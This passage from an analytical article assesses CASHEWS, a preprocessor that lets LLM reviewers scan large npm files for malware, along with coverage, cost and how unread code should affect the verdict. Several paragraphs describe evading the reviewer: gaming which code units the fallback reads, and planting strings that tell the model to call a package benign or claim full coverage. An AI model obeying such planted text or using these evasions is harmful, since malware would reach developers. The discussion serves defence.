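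Abbreviation can help even when decoding fails. CASHEWS couldn't unpack a compressed payload in the package regve, but it did shorten the long string that held it. DeepSeek V4 Flash's maliciousness score for the package then rose from 0.3 to 0.9, even though the payload was still compressed.

The next table shows how much each step shortened the 512 files above 25,000 tokens. The last column gives the reduction that a tenth of the files reached or exceeded.

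| Step | Files affected | Median reduction | Top tenth |
|---|---|---|---|
| Decoding | 89.1% | 0.3% | 7.3% |
| Keeping three extracted units | 47.7% | 43.3% | 98.9% |
| Slicing | 27.3% | 0.6% | 23.4% |
| Abbreviation | 91.8% | 19.3% | 75.7% |

Slicing contributed little in CASHEWS, which sliced only 140 of the 512 files. Another 239 were too complex to slice, including 63 of the 166 malicious ones. This contrasts sharply with the 93.7% that Nguyen and colleagues report, but the results are compatible because Nguyen's team left out the packages it couldn't slice, while CASHEWS passed such files on unsliced. Slicing alone still seems unlikely to solve the problem of large files, because the largest are often too complex to slice.

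### Results on large files

After all four steps, 110 of the 512 large files were still too large for most of the reviewers. For these, CASHEWS falls back to sending the model only the three units with the most sources and sinks.

Noirot Ferrand and colleagues tested the same six reviewers as in their baseline, which used unprocessed code. The table shows the share of the 166 large malicious files that each reviewer missed.

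| Reviewer | Unprocessed | Shortened | Shortened, with fallback |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single call, GPT-5 nano | 36.7% | 27.7% | 21.1% |
| Single call, GPT-5.6 Luna | 34.9% | 26.5% | 19.3% |
| Single call, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 34.3% | 24.1% | 15.7% |
| Three stages, GPT-5 nano | 30.1% | 21.1% | 16.3% |
| Three stages, GPT-5.6 Luna | 28.3% | 22.3% | 20.5% |
| Three stages, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 40.4% | 29.5% | 22.3% |

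The largest improvement was 18.6 percentage points, for the single-call reviewer with DeepSeek V4 Flash, which missed 26 malicious files instead of 57. Coverage rose from 69.1–85.7% to 98.8–100%.

In those coverage figures, Noirot Ferrand and colleagues count a file as covered if the detector can scan it, even when the fallback sends only three of its units. In a tenth of the files with extracted units, keeping three of them discards at least 98.9% of the tokens. The share of code that the model reads is therefore well below 100%.

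The fallback also seems to miss most of the malware in the files that need it. With a single call, it cut missed files by 11 to 14, depending on the model. If malicious files were as common among these 110 files as among all the large files, about 36 were malicious, so the fallback caught roughly a third. The researchers found that it missed some payloads in large bundles because the malicious unit had sources and sinks but ranked fourth. False positives rose by up to 1.7 percentage points.

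Reading more than three units would often add few tokens, since the median unit is about 250 tokens, although some exceed a million characters. Limiting total tokens instead of the number of units would let the reviewer read many more when the units are small.

Most of the improvement came from reading files that had gone unread. Before the fallback, shortening reduced the single-call reviewers' misses by 46 across the three models. In a separate comparison of verdicts on the same files before and after shortening, it corrected 27 misses and caused 18 new ones, a net gain of nine. If that comparison covers the large files, as the small numbers suggest, about four-fifths of the 46 came from higher c and a fifth from higher d. For the three-stage reviewers, shortening corrected 16 misses and caused 13.

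The researchers tried three score thresholds and chose 0.5 because it gave the best net result. At 0.8, shortening would have corrected 10 misses in the three-stage reviewers and caused 27 new ones. The published results may therefore be slightly better than an operator would see on new files.

### Why small files should stay as they are

Across all 4,884 files, shortening increased the number of missed malicious files in three of the six set-ups. The last column of the next table, calculated from the published rates, shows what would happen if CASHEWS processed only files above 25,000 tokens. Both columns for shortened files include the fallback.

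| Reviewer | No files shortened | All files shortened | Only large files shortened |
|---|---|---|---|
| Single call, GPT-5 nano | 7.2% | 6.4% | 6.1% |
| Single call, GPT-5.6 Luna | 7.3% | 8.0% | 6.2% |
| Single call, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 11.5% | 10.8% | 10.2% |
| Three stages, GPT-5 nano | 10.5% | 14.1% | 9.6% |
| Three stages, GPT-5.6 Luna | 9.5% | 13.1% | 9.0% |
| Three stages, DeepSeek V4 Flash | 10.6% | 10.0% | 9.4% |

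For the three-stage reviewer with GPT-5 nano, the miss rate on smaller files rose from about 9% to 14%, which outweighed the improvement on large ones. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues don't explain why. Abbreviation may sometimes remove a string that points to malicious behavior, and decoded code may look less suspicious than obfuscated code. A small file already fits in the window, so shortening it can't raise c, but it can lower d by removing evidence.

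The researchers say that CASHEWS is primarily for large files and that running it on every file would raise costs and worsen detection. Skipping small files would avoid the extra misses in all six set-ups, though the best size threshold might differ in another collection.

### A lower price per file and a higher bill

Noirot Ferrand and colleagues report a net saving of 34.6%, but with the fallback, the bill for Luna's single-call reviews of the large files rose from $6.26 to $12.07. Both figures can be right because they cover different files. The scan of the unprocessed code skipped 155 of the 512 files, which cost nothing. Shortening cut the bill for the other 357 files from $6.26 to $4.42, but reading the 155 previously skipped files added $7.65.

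The 34.6% is an estimate based on input tokens, after subtracting the cost of running CASHEWS. For files that the reviewers could read with or without CASHEWS, the actual model bills fell by 14% to 29%. Part of the difference may be because those bills include the model's answers, which CASHEWS doesn't shorten.

The extra cost was worth paying in this test, since Luna caught 26 more malicious files for an additional $5.81, or about 22 cents each. The cost per detection would be much higher on npm, where far fewer large files are malicious than in the test, in which about a third were.

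Shortening also makes better models affordable. One file in a design-system package shrank from more than 200,000 tokens to under 10,000. Reviewing the shortened version with Luna would cost half as much as reviewing the original with GPT-5 nano, and the same was true of 12.7% of the files.

CASHEWS took a median of 30 seconds to process files above 25,000 tokens and about three minutes for files above 250,000. At the paper's rate of 4.5 cents per core-hour, 30 seconds on one processor core costs less than a twentieth of a cent. Processing costs more than it saves only for files below 1,000 tokens.

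### An attacker who knows the method

Noirot Ferrand and colleagues assume that attackers will study CASHEWS. They discuss how attackers might respond, but didn't test CASHEWS against such attacks. One risk is a file designed to use so much computing time that it delays other reviews. CASHEWS therefore limits the time, memory and output of every step. If a file exceeds a limit, CASHEWS skips that step or returns a partial result instead of abandoning the file. This protects the scanner, but the file may still be too large for the model, in which case the reviewer has to use the fallback.

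An attacker could also try to make CASHEWS remove the payload. The slicer depends on a list of sinks, and it may discard harmful code that uses an operation missing from the list. The rule for files with no sinks doesn't help if the same file also contains a recognised sink. The researchers propose extending the list and using more precise analysis. This would take longer, but they consider that acceptable because slicing currently takes a median of 8.5 seconds.

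Abbreviating long strings has a similar weakness, since the omitted middle may contain the part that matters. CASHEWS could keep any text that looks like JavaScript, but attackers could then use such text to inflate the token count again or to give the model misleading instructions.

The fallback may be easier to exploit than either, because the attacker controls how many sources and sinks each unit contains and can therefore influence which three units the model reads. The researchers say unit selection needs more work but don't discuss this attack. One partial defence is to keep all the code CASHEWS removes and run ordinary detection rules over it. If a rule matches, the reviewer has a reason to send the removed code to the model.

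## How should unread code count in the verdict?

Sampling, shortening and following the execution chain all leave some code unread, but the reviewer still has to return a verdict. It can treat the unread code as harmless, block the package, or report that the review is incomplete and list the code it didn't read.

The choice matters even when coverage is high. Suppose a scanner receives 100,000 files a day and reads 96.8% of them, as the single-call reviewers did when Noirot Ferrand and colleagues gave them unprocessed code. That leaves 3,200 files unread each day. According to GitHub, hundreds of the more than 30,000 packages published on npm each day, or roughly 1%, contain malicious code. If a package has ten files on average and a malicious package has one bad file, about one file in 1,000 is malicious. The 3,200 unread files would include about three malicious ones.

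### Treating unread code as harmless

This policy lets all 3,200 files through without delay, including the three malicious ones. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues adopt it to avoid checking files by hand. At ten minutes per file, checking 3,200 files a day would take 533 hours, the work of about 67 people.

Antivirus software has long worked this way. ClamAV, an open-source virus scanner, stops at its size limit and marks the file "OK", according to a patch to its manual on Open Build Service. NetApp's *Can the file support bypassing virus scan if the maximum file size* explains that the company's storage system releases oversized files unscanned even if an administrator has made scanning mandatory. Oracle's *Maximum file size to scan* justifies skipping such files because they are probably databases or something similar, and unlikely to be programs. That reasoning fails on npm, where the 4.5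 MB payload in the package ai-sdk-ollama was a program.

The estimate of three also assumes that malware is as common in unread files as in the files the scanner reads. Once attackers learn that the scanner clears whatever it can't read, they have a reason to make their files too large to read, and the estimate becomes too low.

### Blocking it

Blocking removes that incentive, because a payload too large to read never reaches anyone. But in the example, blocking also stops about 1,000 harmless files for every malicious one. GitHub warns that even a 1% false-positive rate would disrupt hundreds of legitimate npm releases a day. The same developers would be blocked repeatedly, since a project that ships a large bundle usually ships one in every release.

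Operators who block oversized files come under pressure to raise the limit. The guide *asset-manager*, last updated in January 2025, describes how the British government's website scans uploads with ClamAV. An upload that exceeds the scanner's limits causes an "InfectedFile" error, and the guide says staff will probably need to increase the limits. Changing a setting lets a virus scanner process larger files, but it can't enlarge the context window of an LLM reviewer's model.

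A company that installs a few new packages a week can block packages more readily than a registry can, and it can block them temporarily. *GitHub's npm package firewall can block brand-new versions before they install* (Zorz, 2026) describes a new firewall that checks npm packages against a company's policy before installation and can refuse brand-new versions for a waiting time the company sets. Dependabot, GitHub's tool for updating dependencies, now waits at least three days before proposing a routine update but still proposes security fixes immediately.

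Help Net Security's *GitHub delays version updates so malware gets caught first* (2026) cites a review of 21 widely reported attacks. In every one, someone caught the malicious version within hours. Carlin Cherry, a product manager at GitHub, says that delaying updates does little against dormant backdoors, sabotage by a maintainer or a compromised build system. A delay also helps only if somebody else reads the code in the meantime. If every scanner skips the same large file, three days may pass without anyone learning more about it.

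### Reporting it as not fully reviewed

The third policy keeps the finding separate from the decision about what to do. ClamAV has an optional setting that reports a file over its limits as "Heuristics.Limits.Exceeded FOUND". According to the manual patch on Open Build Service, this does not imply an infection, and other software has to be able to handle the message. If that software has only two categories, the result can be an error like "InfectedFile" on the government's website. An LLM reviewer therefore needs a third verdict value, and the programs that receive the verdict must recognise it.

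The stated reason for a skip can also be wrong or incomplete. In December 2025, a ClamAV user reported that a scan had reached its two-minute time limit, but the program gave the size limit as the reason and counted one infected file. According to Snyder, in *A MAJOR problem with "remote" scanning using ClamAV*, the program had recorded both limits but reported only one. An operator who then raised the size limit could hit the time limit again.

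This policy creates follow-up work. If 3,200 files a day go into a queue that nobody reads, the operator ends up releasing or blocking them, so most need an automatic next step, such as shortening. The CASHEWS preprocessor raised the single-call reviewers' coverage of all files to 97.7%, and its three-piece fallback raised it to 99.9%. Out of 100,000 files, the model would judge 97,700 from their original or shortened code and 2,200 from three pieces each. The remaining 100 would take two people about a day to check.

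Judging by the costs in that test, shortening only files above 25,000 tokens would raise the scanner's daily bill for GPT-5.6 Luna by about $120. Harmless files were more often large in the test, and they are far more common on npm, so both the bill and the number of unread files would probably be higher there.

### What a coverage report should contain

A report that counts only files would list those 2,200 files as covered, even if the model received only a tiny fraction of their code. A usable report counts tokens as well as files and lists partly read files separately.

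| Entry | What to record |
|---|---|
| Files and tokens | How much the model received in full, in part and not at all |
| Skipped code | Each path, its size, and every limit or rule that excluded it |
| Entry points | Which ones the reviewer followed to the end, and each step it could not resolve |
| Model calls | Failures, timeouts, fallbacks to another model, and unusable answers |
| Other checks | Whether hash lookups and detection rules ran on every file |

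Unusable answers belong in the report because software can easily record them as verdicts. The prompt that Noirot Ferrand and colleagues used asks for only two numbers in a fixed format. If a model replies in prose instead, a carelessly written program might record the missing score as zero, which means harmless. A reviewer should retry such a call and, if it fails again, count the code as unread.

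Unresolved steps can also be evidence of malice. CASHEWS found 233 files in which code leading to a sink could generate and run new code, and 205 of them were malicious. The collection had equal numbers of malicious and harmless files, so this feature was 7.3 times as common in the malicious ones. If one file in 1,000 is malicious, finding this feature in a file raises the chance that the file is malicious from 0.1% to about 0.7%. That would justify reading the file next but not blocking it.

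The report of what the model has read should come from the logs of the software that runs it. The model's own account can draw only on what is in its context window, where compaction may have replaced a file with a summary. The code under review can also influence that account. Noirot Ferrand and colleagues give an example of a string in a program that instructs the model to describe the package as benign. A similar string could instruct it to report that it had read every file. Neither string can change a log that the model can't write to. The case for logs therefore doesn't depend on how often models overstate what they have read.

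The log should record which code each call contained, including the call that produced the verdict, not just which files the model requested. Even then, the log can't show whether the model understood that code.

### The time limit on npm

A registry that scans packages before release has to decide how long publishers will wait. In July 2026, npm announced that it would scan every new package before anyone could install it. GitHub's *npm publish-time malware scanning and dual-use metadata* (2026) gives a typical delay of about five minutes, rising to 15 minutes or more at busy times or for some packages, with neither figure guaranteed. After the scan, npm can publish the package, block it or hold it for manual review. Holding it would suit a package that is not fully reviewed, but GitHub doesn't explain in the announcement how npm treats code that its scanner can't read.

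Some LLM reviews finish within five minutes. Doutre and colleagues report that in May, Datadog's system detected a malicious release of the node-ipc package within five minutes, and that customers had the result less than 50 minutes later. Reading a huge package in chunks can also be quick if the calls run in parallel. Other methods take longer. CASHEWS spent more than 322 seconds on decoding alone for one in 20 of the large files it decoded.

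OpenSourceMalware's *NPM Implements Pre-Publication Malware Scanning, But Will It Work?* argues that a five-minute limit leaves too little time to learn much from running packages in isolation. OpenSourceMalware also criticizes npm for not publishing a detection rate or false-positive rate. It notes that GitHub said in April that a person confirmed every detection, and infers that npm must now block packages automatically. That may be right, but the five-minute limit doesn't prove it, because npm can hold a suspicious package for longer while a person looks at it.

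The author expected the scan to catch at least the obvious cases, including malware that reused the Shai-Hulud worm unchanged. Four packages containing an unchanged copy of the worm appeared on npm on September 7. ITPro's *Is Shai-Hulud back?* quotes Charlie Eriksen of Aikido Security, who found that the payload had the same hash as one from an attack in May. According to registry records cited by the security company Corgea (2026), the attacker published all four within about a second, and npm replaced them with harmless placeholders nearly four and a half hours later.

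This was a missed hash match, not evidence of context exhaustion. Ordinary software can compare hashes for a file of any size without a model reading it. Eriksen calls the comparison "a lookup, not a hard problem". npm did not respond to ITPro before publication, so we don't know whether the lookup failed, never ran or lacked that hash. A coverage report that recorded the lookup would help npm tell these cases apart.

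### One review from start to finish

Suppose a new npm package has 1,200 files containing 6 million tokens of code, and the operator lets a model read 500,000 tokens, counting each token once. That is 8.3% of the package. The reviewer could spend the budget like this:

| Step | Model tokens | What it covers |
|---|---|---|
| Manifest and file list | 25,000 | Names, sizes and types of all 1,200 files |
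| Results of a complete pass | 10,000 | Hash lookups and detection rules on every file |
| Execution chain | 200,000 | 79 files, read in full |
| Slices | 105,000 | One bundle of 3 million tokens, also on the chain |
| Rule matches | 50,000 | 20 files outside the chain, read in full |
| Random sample | 110,000 | 44 of the other 1,100 files, read in full |

Ordinary software scans the whole package, because even a cheap model would have to read all 6 million tokens to do so. The reviewing model receives only a list of matches from this scan. With space set aside for that list and the file list, the model reads 465,000 tokens of code, or 7.8% of the package.

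Suppose the model finds nothing malicious and every call succeeds. However, one file on the execution chain, lib/load.js, decodes some text and runs it as a program, and the reviewer can't recover the text. The verdict should then read something like this:

> The code was not fully reviewed. The reviewer read 465,000 of 6,000,000 tokens (7.8%) and found no malicious code in them. It read 143 files in full and 105,000 of the 3,000,000 tokens in dist/vendor.js. It did not open 1,056 files, which are listed separately. One issue is unresolved: lib/load.js runs text that it decodes. Hash lookups and rules were completed on all files and found no known malware. No calls failed.

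A verdict of "harmless" would be too strong, because the hidden text could be the payload or could load any of the 1,056 unopened files. "Malicious" would also be wrong, since harmless packages sometimes run decoded text.

The 7.8% is not the chance that the model has read the payload, if there is one. Suppose a payload has a 70% chance of being in the files that the reviewer chose to read in full, a 20% chance of being in the bundle and a 10% chance of being in the other 1,100 files. If slicing keeps a payload in the bundle 70% of the time, then

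c = 0.7 + 0.2 × 0.7 + 0.1 × 0.04 ≈ 0.84

If the model recognises 90% of the payloads it reads, it has a 76% chance of detecting the payload, and a clean result reduces the odds that the package is malicious by about three-quarters. But these figures depend almost entirely on the assumed 70%. An attacker who knew the procedure might be able to put the payload among the 1,100 other files and have the hidden text load it. The model would then read the payload only if it fell in the random sample, which has a 4% chance of happening.

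The operator should next run lib/load.js in isolation and capture the decoded text. Reading the other 5.5 million tokens in chunks would cost about $1.11 at Luna's rate of $0.20 per million input tokens, excluding instructions and answers. That is too much to spend on every package in a registry, but cheap for one that a company is about to install. The company should hold the package until both the run and the reading are complete.
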